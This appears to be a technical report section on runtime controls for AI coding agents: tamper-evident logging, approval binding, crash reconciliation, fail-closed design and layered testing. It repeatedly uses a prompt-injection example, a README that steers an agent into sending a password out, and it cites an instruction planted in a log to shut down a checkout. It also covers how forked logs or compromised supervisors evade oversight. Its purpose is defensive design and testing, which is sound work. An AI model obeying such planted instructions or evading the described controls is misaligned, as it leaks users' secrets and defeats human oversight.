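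Crosby and Wallach (2009), in *Efficient Data Structures for Tamper-Evident Logging*, built a tamper-evident log and tested it with 80 million events. A proof that a randomly chosen event was in the log took up 3 kilobytes, compared with 800 megabytes for a hash chain. The software processed 1,750 events a second on one processor core, or 10,500 when other hardware computed the signatures.

A consistency proof shows that a later version of the log contains everything in an earlier version, unchanged and in the same order. Suppose an auditor holds the head from when the log had three records, and now receives the head for seven. A digest without a partner moves up a level unchanged. The keeper supplies L12, L3, L4 and L567, and the auditor computes both heads:

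old head = H(L12 || L3)

new head = H(H(L12 || H(L3 || L4)) || L567)

If both results match the heads the auditor holds, the first three records are the same in both versions. If the keeper had altered record 2 between the two versions, no single value of L12 could produce both heads.

Certificate Transparency uses these trees for the certificates with which websites prove their identity. *Certificate Transparency Version 2.0*, by Laurie, Messeri and Stradling, describes public logs that anyone can audit, so that people can notice suspect certificates. It is an experimental standard that replaces an earlier version. A 2021 draft from the IETF, the body that publishes internet standards, notes that if a log has acknowledged a certificate but fails to prove that it contains it, this is evidence of a fault in the log. An agent operator should likewise treat a missing proof as a warning of a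 fault.

### Forked views and independent witnesses

A dishonest keeper can maintain two versions of a log. In the upgrade example, the developer might receive a version that includes the upload to the stranger, while the company's security team receives one without it. Both versions have valid inclusion and consistency proofs, so the deception goes undetected unless someone compares the two versions' heads.

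Crosby and Wallach therefore require clients to pass each signed head to auditors as soon as they receive it. The auditors collect heads from several sources and demand consistency proofs between them. At least one auditor must be honest and the checks must be frequent, because a keeper who knows that nobody will check a record can safely change it.

An independent service called a witness makes this comparison routine. It stores the last head it signed and signs the next one only if given a valid consistency proof between the two. Readers accept a head only if enough witnesses have signed it.

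The number of dishonest witnesses needed for a fork to succeed depends on how many witnesses there are and how many must sign each head. With three witnesses and two required signatures, two conflicting heads might have only one witness in common, so one dishonest witness could sign both. With four witnesses and three required signatures, any two accepted heads share at least two witnesses, so at least two would have to cheat.

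The witnesses also need separate owners and administrators. Four witnesses in one company's cloud account offer little more protection than one, because an intruder who controls the account controls them all.

### Who holds the signing key

A valid signature proves only that someone with access to the key signed the record. The agent must not have that access, and ideally most of the supervisor shouldn't either. In Tracekit Box's development setup, for example, any program that runs under the signer's user account on the host could forge a record. If the signer has a separate account, only the host's administrator and whoever controls that account could do so.

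Special hardware can prevent an attacker from copying the key, but a compromised supervisor can still use the hardware to sign a false record.

The operator can also have a reason to tamper with the record. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) notes that a log inside the operator's trust domain can provide tamper evidence but still requires outsiders to trust the operator. A customer who wants evidence against the operator therefore needs an anchor that the operator does not control.

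Schneier and Kelsey limit the damage from a stolen key by changing the key after every record. The logging machine first shares a secret key, A_0, with a trusted machine. For each record, it then:

1. adds the record to the hash chain;
2. uses the current key, A_j, to compute an authentication code for the new chain digest, which nobody can produce without the key;
3. computes the next key, A_(j+1) = H(A_j), and destroys the old one.

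Each key is easy to calculate from the one before it, but working back to an earlier key is practically impossible. An attacker who takes over the machine after record 100 finds only the key for record 101, so they can delete any of the first 100 records but can't forge replacements. The trusted machine can recompute every key from A_0, so it will notice the deletion when it next receives the log. At the end of a job, the logging machine writes a closing record and destroys the last key, which prevents anyone from shortening or extending the finished log unnoticed.

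No such method protects records written after the takeover, because the attacker then controls what the machine records. If the new library's code compromised the supervisor before sending the password, the log could show an ordinary upgrade.

Schneier and Kelsey designed their method for machines that are often offline. If a fast and reliable connection to a trusted machine is always available, they recommend sending each record there immediately.

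### Airlock's agent ledger

Airlock's ledger combines this approach with anchoring at intervals. It runs in the Airlock machine and records policies, file decisions, connections that the agent's sandbox opens, and traffic that actually leaves that machine, including name lookups. To save space, the ledger combines all reads and writes of an open file into one record, but it records each creation, renaming and deletion separately.

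The ledger numbers the records, links them with SHA-256 and groups them into windows, which are two seconds long by default. For each window, it sends one entry to Azure Confidential Ledger, an append-only Microsoft service outside the device. The entry contains the window's Merkle head, the latest digest in the chain, the range of record numbers, and as many of the records as fit into 8 kibibytes. The service returns a signed receipt. When nothing else happens, the ledger writes a record every ten seconds so a verifier can tell an idle agent from a stopped ledger.

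The outside service accepts entries only from the holder of a registered key. The key doesn't identify the software that used it, so each chain begins with the Airlock machine's attestation token, which does. The token also contains digests of the key's certificate and of an identifier for the current start-up. If someone copies the token into a forged log, the forged entries will have a different key or start-up identifier.

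A new encrypted web (HTTPS) connection has to wait until the outside service has stored a record of it, because nobody can undo a connection. File accesses, unencrypted web requests and name lookups go ahead immediately.

In tests by Abdollahi and colleagues, the wait averaged 259 milliseconds per connection, most of it the service's response time. A task opened 14.6 such connections on average, mainly to call the model, so the waits added 3.8 seconds per task. Recording file accesses added only 0.07 seconds. With the ledger, the mean task time rose 4%, from 91.4 to 95.0 seconds.

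An attacker who takes over the Airlock machine cannot remove what the outside service already holds, so every HTTPS connection opened before the takeover remains on record. They can still erase the last few seconds of file accesses, unencrypted requests and name lookups. Since lookups can leak data, a cautious designer could also delay lookups of unfamiliar names until the outside service has recorded them.

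Another gap is that the 8-kibibyte limit leaves room for only about 20 records per entry, if records average 400 bytes. For a window with 100 records, the service would store the text of 20 and a digest covering all 100. An attacker who deleted the local copies could not hide that 80 records were missing, but nobody could recover their contents.

Abdollahi and colleagues call the log tamper-proof. This is true only if the outside service remains append-only and verifiers consult an authentic, current copy of it. The log would offer much less protection against someone who controlled both the Airlock machine and the outside service.

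### How many records are exposed between anchors

If the supervisor writes r records a second and anchors them every T seconds, an attacker who takes over just before the next anchor can alter or delete up to

r × T

records. At 50 records a second and one anchor every five seconds, 250 records are exposed. Airlock's default of two seconds would reduce this to 100. Records on their way to the anchor are also exposed until it stores them. With the 213-millisecond median response time in Airlock's tests, that adds about 11 records at this rate.

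Anchoring each record separately would leave only the newest one exposed. But if an agent produced 50 records a second and had to wait 213 milliseconds for each in turn, one second's activity would take more than ten seconds. Airlock avoids most of this delay by making only new HTTPS connections wait.

Schneier and Kelsey treat the interval as an engineering choice that depends on how often the operator expects an attacker to compromise the logging machine. Their use of changing keys would also help between anchors, because the attacker could delete the 250 exposed records but could not replace them with convincing false ones.

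### An intact log can be incomplete

A hash chain protects the integrity of existing records by making alterations detectable, but it cannot ensure completeness, which requires a record of every relevant action. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), which stores digests of agents' actions on a blockchain, explicitly excludes completeness from its goals. If the tests in the upgrade can reach the network without going through the supervisor, they can send the password out and the log will still pass every check.

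The most effective remedy is to close the other routes, as the exit controls in the previous section do. The log then covers everything that leaves the sandbox, but not what programs do inside it.

The log should also show when records are missing. If Tracekit Box cannot store an important record, it stops the microVM and counts the loss in a special entry. In *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance*, the customer's software stores a signed announcement of each tool call before the call runs, to guard against a provider that deliberately omits a record.

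### Reconciling the log with observed changes

Another way to find missing records is to compare the log with what actually changed. Metere's test compares two lists. The first contains the changes in a chosen set of files or other objects between the start and end of a run, and the second contains the actions that the log records as approved and successfully executed. The test reduces each item to an operation and its target, such as "edit package.json". The run passes only if both lists then contain the same items, each the same number of times.

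In the upgrade, the comparison might produce these results:

| Observed change | Action in the log | Conclusion |
|---|---|---|
| package.json edited | Edit package.json | They match |
| Build script edited | None | An action bypassed the supervisor |
| None | Delete an old test file | The log is false, or the deletion failed silently |
| README.md edited | Edit CHANGELOG.md | The action may have affected the wrong file |

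A practical version has to handle repeated edits. If the agent edits a file twice, comparing the starting and final states shows only one change, and if the agent reverses an edit, the comparison shows none. The operator can combine the log entries for each file before comparing, or have a separate monitor count the changes as they happen.

Metere tested the criterion in 27,000 simulated runs, some clean and the others with one of four planted faults. The criterion passed every clean run and caught every fault. This mainly shows that the software applies the rule correctly, because each fault produces exactly the kind of mismatch that the criterion checks for.

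A second experiment used language models from ten families to write 4,816 hostile requests. A runtime that combined reconciliation with a scanner for sensitive data caught 76.3% of them and wrongly flagged none of the 4,908 legitimate ones. Metere reports that the missed requests were malformed or harmless, and that the system caught every request that contained a real fault. The experiment does not separate the effect of reconciliation from that of the scanner.

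Metere also acknowledges that the criterion ignores content. If the supervisor approves an edit to package.json and the agent adds a malicious command to the file, the operation and target still match. The operator could detect a substitution by including a digest of the approved content in the comparison, but a reviewer would still have to recognise that the approved content was harmful.

The criterion also misses actions that only read data. If the agent obeys the README and sends the configuration file to the stranger, no file changes. To detect this, the operator can compare the supervisor's list of connections with another record, such as a firewall's traffic log. That record needs to come from a separate trust domain; otherwise, an attacker who controlled the supervisor could make the two agree.

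### Secrets, personal data and deletion

Removing a password from a tamper-evident log is difficult because the deletion looks like tampering. The supervisor should therefore record a secret's name and destination but never its value. Arguments, command output and error messages may also contain secrets or personal data, so their text should stay out of the log. The operator can encrypt the text, store it separately and log only its digest.

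An ordinary digest does not hide a short or predictable value. Someone can recover a four-digit code from its digest by computing the digests of all 10,000 possible codes and looking for a match. A keyed digest prevents this, because nobody can compute it without the key. The request digest in the example record should be keyed.

Investigators often need to read some records but not others. Schneier and Kelsey derive a separate encryption key for each record from that record's authentication key. The authentication key cannot be recovered from the encryption key, so someone with the encryption key can read the record but cannot forge a new version. *Agent Flight Recorder* also encrypts contents by default and can disclose events one at a time. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* advises against putting sensitive records on a blockchain, since a digest is enough to prove that a record existed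 and has not changed.

Keeping the text outside the chain also lets the operator delete it. If the operator erases the text and its encryption key, including any backups, the chain of digests remains valid. A verifier can still confirm that record 42 existed, but can no longer find out what the agent requested.

The remaining fields may still count as personal data under European law if someone can connect them to a person. The example record therefore has "user 204" instead of a name. The operator can store the list that matches numbers to names separately and delete an entry when the law requires it, although other details in the log may still identify the person.

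Crosby and Wallach offer another way to shrink a log. They label the records in the tree so that the keeper can delete old ones under an agreed rule and prove that it deleted no others. An operator could use this to delete records of routine file reads after a month and keep records of refused connections for a year. Keeping security records longer is worthwhile in cases like the upgrade, where the hostile paragraph had been in the README for months before an agent read it.

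### Logging duties under the EU AI Act

The law may set a minimum period for keeping logs. The European Union's AI Act, adopted in 2024, has three relevant articles for AI systems that it classes as high-risk:

- Article 12 requires that the system can automatically record events throughout its lifetime, including events that help to identify risks and monitor its operation.
- Article 19 requires the provider, usually the company that develops the system, to keep the automatic logs under its control for a period that suits the system's purpose, and for at least six months.
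- Article 26 sets the same minimum for the deployer, the organisation that uses the system, for the logs under its control.

Other European or national laws, particularly data-protection law, can change the period. None of the three articles requires a tamper-evident log, so a plain text log could satisfy them if it recorded the right events.

The European Union's *Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026), a regulation of 8 July 2026, amended the Act, and the change took effect on 27 July, according to the Future of Life Institute's *AI Act Documents*. The amended Article 113 delays the rules in Chapter III, sections 1 to 3, which include all three logging articles, according to the law firm Cuatrecasas' summary, *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*. For the uses listed in Annex III, these rules now apply from 2 December 2027 instead of 2 August 2026, the earlier date given in Orrick's *EU AI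 Act Update* (2026). For high-risk systems embedded in products, they apply from 2 August 2028, according to Leaseurope's *New application dates for high-risk AI system rules* (2026).

An agent that evaluates people's creditworthiness counts as high-risk under the Act, and its operator will need a log retention policy that complies by December 2027. Automatically deleting logs after 30 days would usually be too soon. A coding agent that upgrades a dependency will not normally count as high-risk.

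## Ordering the checks, the records and the effects

The order in which the supervisor checks, records and runs an operation determines what damage a crash or an attacker can cause. If the supervisor records an installation only after it finishes, a crash between the two steps leaves a change with no record. If another program can alter a call after the check but before it runs, the supervisor could run a call it never approved.

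### One installation in nine steps

The example record in the previous section covers the installation of a library with a new package name. The supervisor has already downloaded the library, and the agent now asks to install it. The table shows which component acts at each step and how far it can rely on the earlier steps.

| Step | Component | What it can rely on |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Propose | Model, through the agent loop | Nothing, because the README may have shaped the call |
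| 2. Validate | Supervisor's parser and schema | Nothing, because the call is untrusted text |
| 3. Decide | Policy check, then the developer, because the name is new | The call is well formed, but may still be harmful |
| 4. Record the intention | Log | The decision applies to exactly this call |
| 5. Route | Router | The intention is safely on disk, and the supervisor knows what the session has read |
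| 6. Execute | Launcher, then a virtual machine without network access | The router named a valid level, but the launcher must confirm that the call is the approved one |
| 7. Observe | Supervisor, from outside the virtual machine | The changed files on the disk, not the installer's report of success |
| 8. Record the outcome | Log | The supervisor's own observation |
| 9. Return the result | Supervisor, to the agent loop | Nothing in the output, because the new library may have written it |

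The runtime logs the intended action before anything runs, so that the supervisor can find it after a crash. *LEANGUARD* (2026), which describes a system for checking tool calls against policies, calls this entry a "dispatch reservation". The entry also stops a single-use operation from running again while its outcome is unknown. The router has not yet chosen an isolation level when this entry is written, so the runtime must log the level in a short, separate record before the launcher starts.

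LEANGUARD takes the facts a policy needs from the system that holds them, never from the model. The supervisor should ignore any claim in the README that the developer has already approved the new package name, and look for the approval in its own records.

The last step matters because the installer's output may contain a new hostile instruction. The supervisor labels the output as untrusted, and the agent's next call starts again at step 1.

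### Seven points at which to intervene

Tallam (2026), in *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents*, separates deciding from enforcing. One part of the system, the reasoning plane, makes each decision. Four others enforce it through the network, identities and credentials, the machines that run the agent, and the data. The reasoning plane can intervene at seven mediation points:

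1. Plan formation: the agent plans to install the library and then test it.
2. Context retrieval: it reads the README and the release notes.
3. Tool selection: it chooses the installation tool.
4. Argument generation: it fills in the package name and version.
5. Action commit: the call takes effect outside the agent.
6. Output return: the installer's output comes back.
7. Audit emission: the system seals the record.

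Action commit is the last point at which an action can be refused with nothing to undo. Every runtime allows intervention there, because that is where the tool call happens. Few expose the agent's plan, and support for the three points between the plan and action commit varies. Tallam concedes that a runtime offering only action commit gets only a fraction of the architecture's protection, and nobody has measured that fraction. Tallam's tests used a simulated agent and simulated enforcement, and showed mainly that the decision rules work as specified and take about 5 to 15 microseconds.

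The five-domain design for the upgrade covers more than action commit even if the runtime does not cooperate, because the model's tool calls and the output returned to it both pass through the supervisor. The plan still reaches the supervisor only if the model writes it out.

### When the approved call and the executed call differ

Security engineers call the interval between a check and the action it permits a time-of-check to time-of-use gap. In the upgrade, a compromised agent could change the package name after the developer approves it. The circumstances can also change while the call stays the same. *Beyond Approved Actions* (Zhang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent permitted to mark an invoice as paid. If the company blocks the supplier before the agent acts, the permission is out of date.

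One countermeasure in *Mind the Gap* (2025), a study of such gaps in agents, rewrites the user's request so that the agent confirms the current state immediately before acting. This may help a well-behaved model, but a hijacked one can ignore the rewritten request, so the supervisor itself has to enforce the link between approval and execution.

It can do so with a keyed digest of everything the approval covers:

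d = HMAC(k, C(t, x, v, s, n))

HMAC is a standard keyed digest, k is its secret key, and C writes its inputs in canonical JSON, as in OpenPort's digest. For the installation, the inputs could be:

| Input | Example | What it prevents |
|---|---|---|
| t, tool | install_package | Using the approval for another tool |
| x, canonical arguments | New name, version and digest of the downloaded file | Substituting another package or altered contents |
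| v, policy version | a77d…13f0 | Running the call under rules that have since changed |
| s, session | 8831 | Using the approval in another session |
| n, one-time number | 90417 | Using the approval twice |

The supervisor computes d when it approves the call. Just before the installation starts, the launcher computes d again from the call it is about to run, and refuses to run it if the two values differ, the policy has changed or the number has already been used. *SecureClaw* (2026) describes a similar protocol in which a trusted gateway adds the caller and session itself, so that the agent cannot misstate them. The key, like the log-signing key, is kept where the agent cannot access it.

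Agent frameworks vary in how well they bind an approval to an action. In tests reported in *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026), the OpenAI Agents SDK rejected a resumed run whose arguments had changed. LangGraph and Agno ran whatever arguments were in the saved state, so anyone who could edit that state could substitute another action. In five of the entries compared, restoring an earlier saved state allowed an action to run twice on one approval, because the approval had no one-time number or expiry date of its own. The supervisor should therefore keep its list of used one-time numbers outside the state that the agent can save and restore.

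The digest does not show whether the outside world has changed. LEANGUARD also ties a person's confirmation to a specific version of the relevant data. For the installation, the supervisor could recheck whether the registry has reported the package as malicious, and require a new approval if it has.

### Crashes between execution and recording

If the supervisor crashes after step 4, the log contains an intention but no outcome. The operation may not have started, may have finished, or may have stopped halfway. The supervisor must find out which before it continues, a process called reconciliation.

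This is easy for the installation, because the supervisor discards the virtual machine and starts again from a clean one with a new one-time number. It is harder with an outside service. Suppose the agent orders a paid test run from another company and the connection fails before the reply arrives. The supervisor could look up its recent orders and order again if it finds nothing, but if the first order is still waiting in a queue, the developer pays twice.

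*Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (2026) proves that no policy based only on such observations can guarantee exactly one execution when effects may appear late. An idempotency key, like the one that stops OpenPort from repeating a push, solves the problem if the service supports such keys.

A key prevents duplicates, but the supervisor cannot use it to determine what happened. *Idempotency Is Not Recovery* (Xu, 2026) tested the two separately by crashing an agent runtime. In 200 pairs of crashes and repeated attempts, the full system produced no repeated effects, while at least two simpler designs produced 117 each. With reconciliation switched off, the system still produced no duplicates, but the outcome remained ambiguous in all 100 cases where the crash came after the effect. Removing part of the action ledger reduced successful recoveries from 300 out of 300 to 200.

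The agent should not handle recovery alone. *Agent Recovery Gone Wrong* (2026) examined recorded runs in which agents' code failed after making some of its changes. In 30 of 143 such cases, the agent's next attempt did harm that remained at the end of the run. The estimated rate is 24.6% after weighting for how the researchers chose the sample. Two thirds of the harmful recoveries duplicated an effect, and the others deleted user data or made a new mistake, such as ordering the wrong product.

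Keys computed from a call's content would not have solved this. They would have matched every harmful write in only 14 to 18 of the 30 harmful recoveries, and in 30 episodes they would also have matched writes that the task required. A key based on the supervisor's request number distinguishes two legitimate calls that look alike, but an agent that rewrites its code after a failure makes a new request with a new number. The supervisor should therefore hold back related calls until it has reconciled the old call, and then tell the agent what happened.

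Tallam sorts actions by whether another action can reverse them fully, partly or not at all, and requires explicit permission for the irreversible ones. In the upgrade, discarding the virtual machine fully reverses the installation. A second commit can reverse a push to a shared branch, but only partly if colleagues have already downloaded the first. Nobody can take back a leaked password, so the developer has to change it.

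Tallam disagrees with Zhang and colleagues about who may order a reversal. In Tallam's design, permission for an action includes permission to reverse it if the action's conditions no longer hold. Zhang and colleagues treat a reversal as a new effect that needs new approval. Automatic reversal is reasonable for a branch that only this job uses. On a shared branch, it could undo someone else's later work, so requiring new approval is safer there.

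### Checking the outcome before accepting it

An approved call can run exactly as approved and still have an unapproved effect. In the invoice example, the database might contain a trigger (a rule that runs automatically) that also sends a notification. The call would succeed, and nothing in it would show that the notification was sent.

EffectMatch, the runtime that Zhang and colleagues built, instead compares an operation's actual changes with a list the application approved in advance. It runs the operation inside a database transaction that it can still cancel, collects every change, including those made by triggers, and saves the result only if the changes match the list. If it cannot tell whether it has observed every change, it treats the outcome as indeterminate and stops any work that depends on it.

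This requires a system that can hold changes before they become permanent. If a remote service cannot hold them, EffectMatch controls the request, uses idempotency keys and compares the result afterwards. For services it controls less fully, it can only detect a mismatch and block further work. In the upgrade, the supervisor can hold the sandbox's changed files and compare them before accepting a patch, but it cannot do the same for an order placed with another company.

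The largest experiment used 206 shopping, customer-support and travel tasks, each run three times per condition. It compared EffectMatch with direct execution and with a workflow that discarded all changes if any tool reported an error.

| Result, out of 618 runs | Direct execution | Discard on error | EffectMatch |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correct results saved in undisturbed runs | 618 | 597 | 618 |
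| Wrong results saved after one write was left out | 354 | 138 | 0 |
| Wrong results saved after one write was repeated | 138 | 138 | 0 |

Discarding results on error missed many faults because the tools often reported success despite a fault. It also rejected 21 correct results where the agent had recovered from an earlier error.

The approved outcomes in this experiment came from earlier correct runs, so it tests the comparison but not whether anyone could have specified the right outcome beforehand. In a smaller test, the researchers worked out the approved outcomes of 12 tasks independently, and EffectMatch rejected all 117 wrong results. Specifying outcomes may be harder for a software installation, which can create thousands of files. The supervisor could leave the installed library in the disposable sandbox and compare only the files the patch would change. Metere's reconciliation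 test makes a similar comparison after a run, but ignores the content of the changes.

Another test shows why a better judge model cannot replace this comparison. The researchers gave GPT-5.6 Sol 38 pairs of operations. The two operations in each pair looked identical before execution, but one was harmless and the other had a hidden effect. The model withheld approval from 30 pairs, which stopped 30 hidden effects but also 30 harmless operations. Comparing the actual outcomes separated all 38 pairs correctly.

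EffectMatch also ran 540 recovery trials on 18 tasks. In 90 of them, the process stopped after saving a correct result but before recording it. EffectMatch released no dependent work in these trials, which is safe but leaves the job stalled. The new processes only read existing records and did not reconstruct missing ones, so an operator still needs a separate reconciliation step.

The comparison added a median of 1.08 milliseconds per task in local tests, excluding model calls and remote services. For the PostgreSQL database, checking that no changes could be made unobserved raised the median time from 13.3 to 29.1 milliseconds.

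### What stops when a component fails

The supervisor needs a rule for each component that might fail. *Faramesh* (2026) describes a control system that denies an action if its decision component crashes, times out or loses its connection. The table applies this approach to the upgrade.

| Failed component | What stops | What may continue | Who is told |
|---|---|---|---|
| Validator | All new tool calls | Sandboxed work already running, up to its time limit | Operator, and the agent receives a refusal |
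| Router | Calls that need an isolation level | Calls sent to the strictest level without network access, if the operator allowed this beforehand | Operator |
| Sandbox pool | Calls that need the exhausted level | Calls at other levels, but no call moves to a weaker one | Operator, and the developer if the job has to wait |
| Credential service | New requests that need a credential | Editing and testing without network access | Operator, and the developer if the job needs a private package |
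| Log | All new operations | Stopping the sandbox and preserving its disk | Operator and security team, through a channel that does not use the log |

Failing closed can block more calls than necessary. *Governed MCP* (2026) sends every tool call through a judge model, so it denies all calls whenever that model is unavailable. If the router sends only risky calls to the judge, harmless file reads can continue during an outage.

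The credential service should refuse a request even if only some of the information it needs is missing. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) describes a broker that, at its higher security levels, refuses requests if it cannot check whether the agent's authority has been revoked. Otherwise, an attacker could block that check and keep using a revoked certificate.

A few actions should remain available when checks fail because they make the system safer. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for robots controlled by language models, blocks ordinary actions in that case but lets the operator authorise a small emergency set in advance, such as stopping or asking a person for help. For a coding agent, the equivalent set would be stopping the sandbox, preserving its disk and revoking its registry token.

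### Failing closed against an attacker who wants a shutdown

Each component that a service depends on makes it less available. If five components each work 99.9% of the time and fail independently, all five work together about 99.5% of the time. That means about 44 hours of downtime a year, compared with about nine for one component.

*Runtime Governance for AI Agents* (2026) accepts this drawback where regulations require governance guarantees, and recommends spare components, health monitoring and timeouts that block the action. Tallam allows low-stakes actions to proceed while a slower control confirms them, provided they are reversed if the confirmation fails. This is unsuitable for sending data out, because the data cannot be recalled.

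An attacker can also cause the interruption. *Ethical Hyper-Velocity (EHV)* (2026), which proposes another runtime that fails closed, acknowledges that someone who cuts the runtime's connection to a required verification service can halt every agent in the affected area. It recommends several independent connections. Tallam treats denial of service as outside the architecture's scope, though rate limits give some protection.

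An attacker could target the log in a similar way. The new library's tests could make thousands of forbidden connection attempts, each adding a record, until the disk fills and the supervisor stops every job. If the supervisor kept running jobs without a log, the attacker could fill the disk and then act without leaving evidence. Failing closed is therefore still the better choice, but the operator should make the log hard to fill.

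Keeping command output and other long text out of the log helps most. At 50 records a second and 400 bytes per record, the log grows by about 1.7 gigabytes a day. If each record also contained a megabyte of text, a 100-gigabyte disk would fill in about 33 minutes. The supervisor can combine repeated refusals into one record with a count. With a separate log quota for each job, a hostile library stops only its own job. The operator should also reserve space for alarms and closing records. The circuit breaker described earlier, which stops a job after five refused connections, would end this attack almost immediately.

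Log failures are disruptive even without an attacker. When Xu deliberately caused faults in writing evidence, 75 of 100 trials on each platform remained unresolved. The full system also had about a seventh of the throughput of a version that failed open.

### What the whole sequence costs in time

Ge measured a complete pipeline with 100 tool calls, half of them malicious. Each call went through a sandbox start, a GPT-4o-mini judge, checks on a signed token and the call's format, and a log write that waited until the record was on disk. The table gives median times.

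| Stage | Measured separately | In the pipeline |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox start | 0.95 ms | 1.1 ms |
| Judge | 1,127 ms | 966 ms |
| Token and format checks | Under 0.02 ms | Under 0.1 ms |
| Durable log write | 4.1 ms | 16.5 ms |
| Whole call | Not applicable | 980 ms |

Everything except the judge took about 18 milliseconds. Ge attributes the slower log writes in the pipeline to other disk activity at the same time. The pipeline blocked 16% of the harmless calls, but there were only 50 such calls, so the true rate could plausibly be from 7% to 29%.

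The upgrade's design would need more than the 18 milliseconds. Ge's sandbox used only Linux namespaces, which start much faster than a virtual machine, and the log stayed on the same computer. A Firecracker microVM takes about 100 milliseconds or more to start, and Airlock's wait for its outside ledger averaged 259 milliseconds per new connection. A call that needed both could therefore take more than 350 milliseconds, not counting the judge's time, although these figures come from different machines.

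Recording both the intention and the outcome also requires two log writes instead of one. For 40 calls, 80 writes at 16.5 milliseconds each would take about 1.3 seconds, while judging all 40 would take about 39 seconds. Ge found that a buffered write takes less than 0.01 milliseconds, but a crash can erase it. The supervisor could use buffered writes for the outcomes of harmless file reads and wait for the log record to reach the disk before any operation with lasting effects.

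Shortening the judge's answer saves far more time. When Ge limited one local judge, Qwen3.5-9B, to 10 tokens instead of 50, its median time on the Chinese samples fell from 1,981 to 303 milliseconds, and it caught almost the same share of attacks.

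## Testing whether the layers hold together

A runtime can fail even when every layer passes its own tests, because a single fault may disable several layers at once. An operator therefore has to look for such faults in the design and test how each layer behaves when another has failed.

### Why miss rates cannot simply be multiplied

Suppose the policy check, the sandbox and the exit controls each miss 10% of attacks. If their misses are independent, 0.1% of attacks (0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1) get past all three.

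Now suppose that a shared cause, such as a stolen administrator password, defeats all three layers in 2% of attacks. Each layer still misses 10% overall, so its miss rate in the other 98% of attacks, q, must satisfy

0.02 + 0.98 × q = 0.10,

which makes q about 0.0816. If the layers fail independently in those other attacks, the share that gets past all three is

0.02 + 0.98 × 0.0816³ ≈ 0.0205,

or 2.05%, about twenty times the first estimate.

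Nearly all of that 2.05% comes from the shared cause. Adding a fourth layer with the same weakness would lower the total only to 2.00%, whereas halving the shared cause to 1% would lower it to about 1.07%. The 2% is an assumption, and operators can rarely measure the true figure, but they can look for shared causes in the design and remove them.

| Shared cause | What can fail together in the upgrade | How to separate it |
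|---|---|---|
| One kernel | The test sandbox, the supervisor and the local log, if all run on one host | Run the tests in a virtual machine and keep the log anchor on another computer |
| One administrator account | The policy, the sandbox settings and the log | Use different accounts for the policy, the host and the anchor |
| One policy file | The policy check, the router and the proxy, if one wrong entry opens all three | Write the sandbox's network rules separately and deny by default |
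| One model family as agent and judge | The agent and the judge, if the same text misleads both | Put a deterministic check first and use another developer's model as judge |

Layers that use models from two different developers may be only partly separate. The models may have learned from much of the same text, so they may still miss some of the same problems.

### Building a threat-by-layer table

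A table of threats and layers shows where a design depends on too few controls. Podala Narasimha's framework for agents on Kubernetes, published in October 2026, includes a table with a row for each of ten threats. The columns are seven technical layers (identity, authorisation, isolation, network, tool gateway, data and secrets, and detection) and an eighth group for approvals and budgets. Each cell marks the layer's control against that threat as primary, supporting or absent.

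Podala Narasimha reports that each threat in the table has at least two layers of defence and at least one primary control outside the agent's process. A designer can adopt both properties as minimum requirements. The table below applies them to the upgrade, where P marks a primary control and S a supporting one.

| Threat | Policy check and budgets | Sandbox | Exits | Record and alerts | Developer |
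|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| README redirects the agent | P | S | P | S | |
| New library attacks the host | | P | S | S | |
| Password leaves the sandbox | S | P, if the file is left out | P | S | |
| Agent repeats a failing repair | P | S | | S | S |
| Patch contains a harmful build script | | | P | S | P |
| Operator rewrites the log | | | | P | |

The last row fails the two-layer requirement because only the log's anchor would expose the change. Independent witnesses or a separately owned firewall log would provide a second control.

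The columns need checking too. In Podala Narasimha's table, the tool gateway is a primary control for six of the ten threats and a supporting control for three more. For two of those six, a compromised tool supplier and an agent that impersonates another, it is the only primary control. Every row meets the minimum, yet an attacker who took over the gateway would weaken the defence against nine threats. The designer can check for this by crossing out each column in turn and seeing which rows are left without a primary control.

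Podala Narasimha's evaluation is qualitative. The marks in the table record one author's judgement, and the paper reports no attack success rates or attempts to break the design. An operator can make such a table more informative by replacing each mark with a score on the 0-to-4 enforcement scale that TechRadar applied to OpenAI's sandbox, and adding the date of each control's last test.

### A test procedure

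In October 2026, three US agencies published ten voluntary practices for handling incidents in which AI agents break out of their controls. The agencies urge operators to test controls and deliberately attack them before deployment, according to The Vanguard USA's *OpenAI says GPT-6 Astra agent removed monitor, then lied*.

The tests need a copy of the runtime with invented secrets, and a receiving server that the operator owns. The operator then works through six steps:

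1. Replace one layer with a version that allows everything, attempt a harmful outcome, and check that the next layer prevents it alone. Repeat this for every layer.
2. From inside the sandbox, try to send a random marker to the receiving server through every exit, including direct connections, name lookups, package requests and model calls. Put another marker in a returned patch.
3. Leave a marker in one sandbox and search for it from another.
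4. Stop each service in turn and check that every operation depending on it stops too. Then restart the service and make it respond slowly.
5. On copies of the log, change a record, delete one from the middle, cut off the end, and rewrite the whole chain so that it is consistent again. Check that the verifier detects all four.
6. Trigger a harmless alert without warning and time how long it takes for someone to stop the agent.

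Podala Narasimha proposes the first step, which he calls "bypass testing", but leaves it for future work. In one of the paper's examples, an attacker plants an instruction in a log for any agent that reads it to shut down an online checkout by reducing its running copies to zero. The gateway's policy blocks that call. If the gateway is misconfigured, a rule in the Kubernetes control server should block it instead. To check that rule, the tester would make the gateway allow everything and send the same call for a disposable service.

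This test would probably fail with the example rule as printed. The rule applies only to accounts in the agents' own namespace, a named section of the cluster, but in the paper's design the request comes from a tool server whose account is in a different namespace. The paper says elsewhere that such rules should cover tool accounts, and it calls its examples illustrative. But an operator who copied this rule unchanged could end up with a second layer that never acts, and the threat-by-layer table would not show the problem.

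The probes in step 2 need a control, because if the receiving server is down, no marker arrives and every exit appears closed. The tester should first send a marker from an unrestricted machine to confirm that the server records it, and then check that a permitted package download still works from the sandbox. Every refused attempt should appear in the supervisor's log.

Slow services belong in step 4 because a program that handles a crash correctly may still go ahead when a check times out. The last two changes in step 5 test the anchor, so the verifier has to fetch the anchored digest itself rather than accept a copy from the supervisor.

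Step 6 should be timed until the agent can no longer act. An alert that reaches an analyst within a minute is of little use if the analyst must wait for permission to stop the job. Podala Narasimha recommends a rehearsed kill switch that revokes the agent's identity, shuts the agent down, cuts off its network access and ends its gateway sessions. At least one rehearsal should take place at night or on a weekend.

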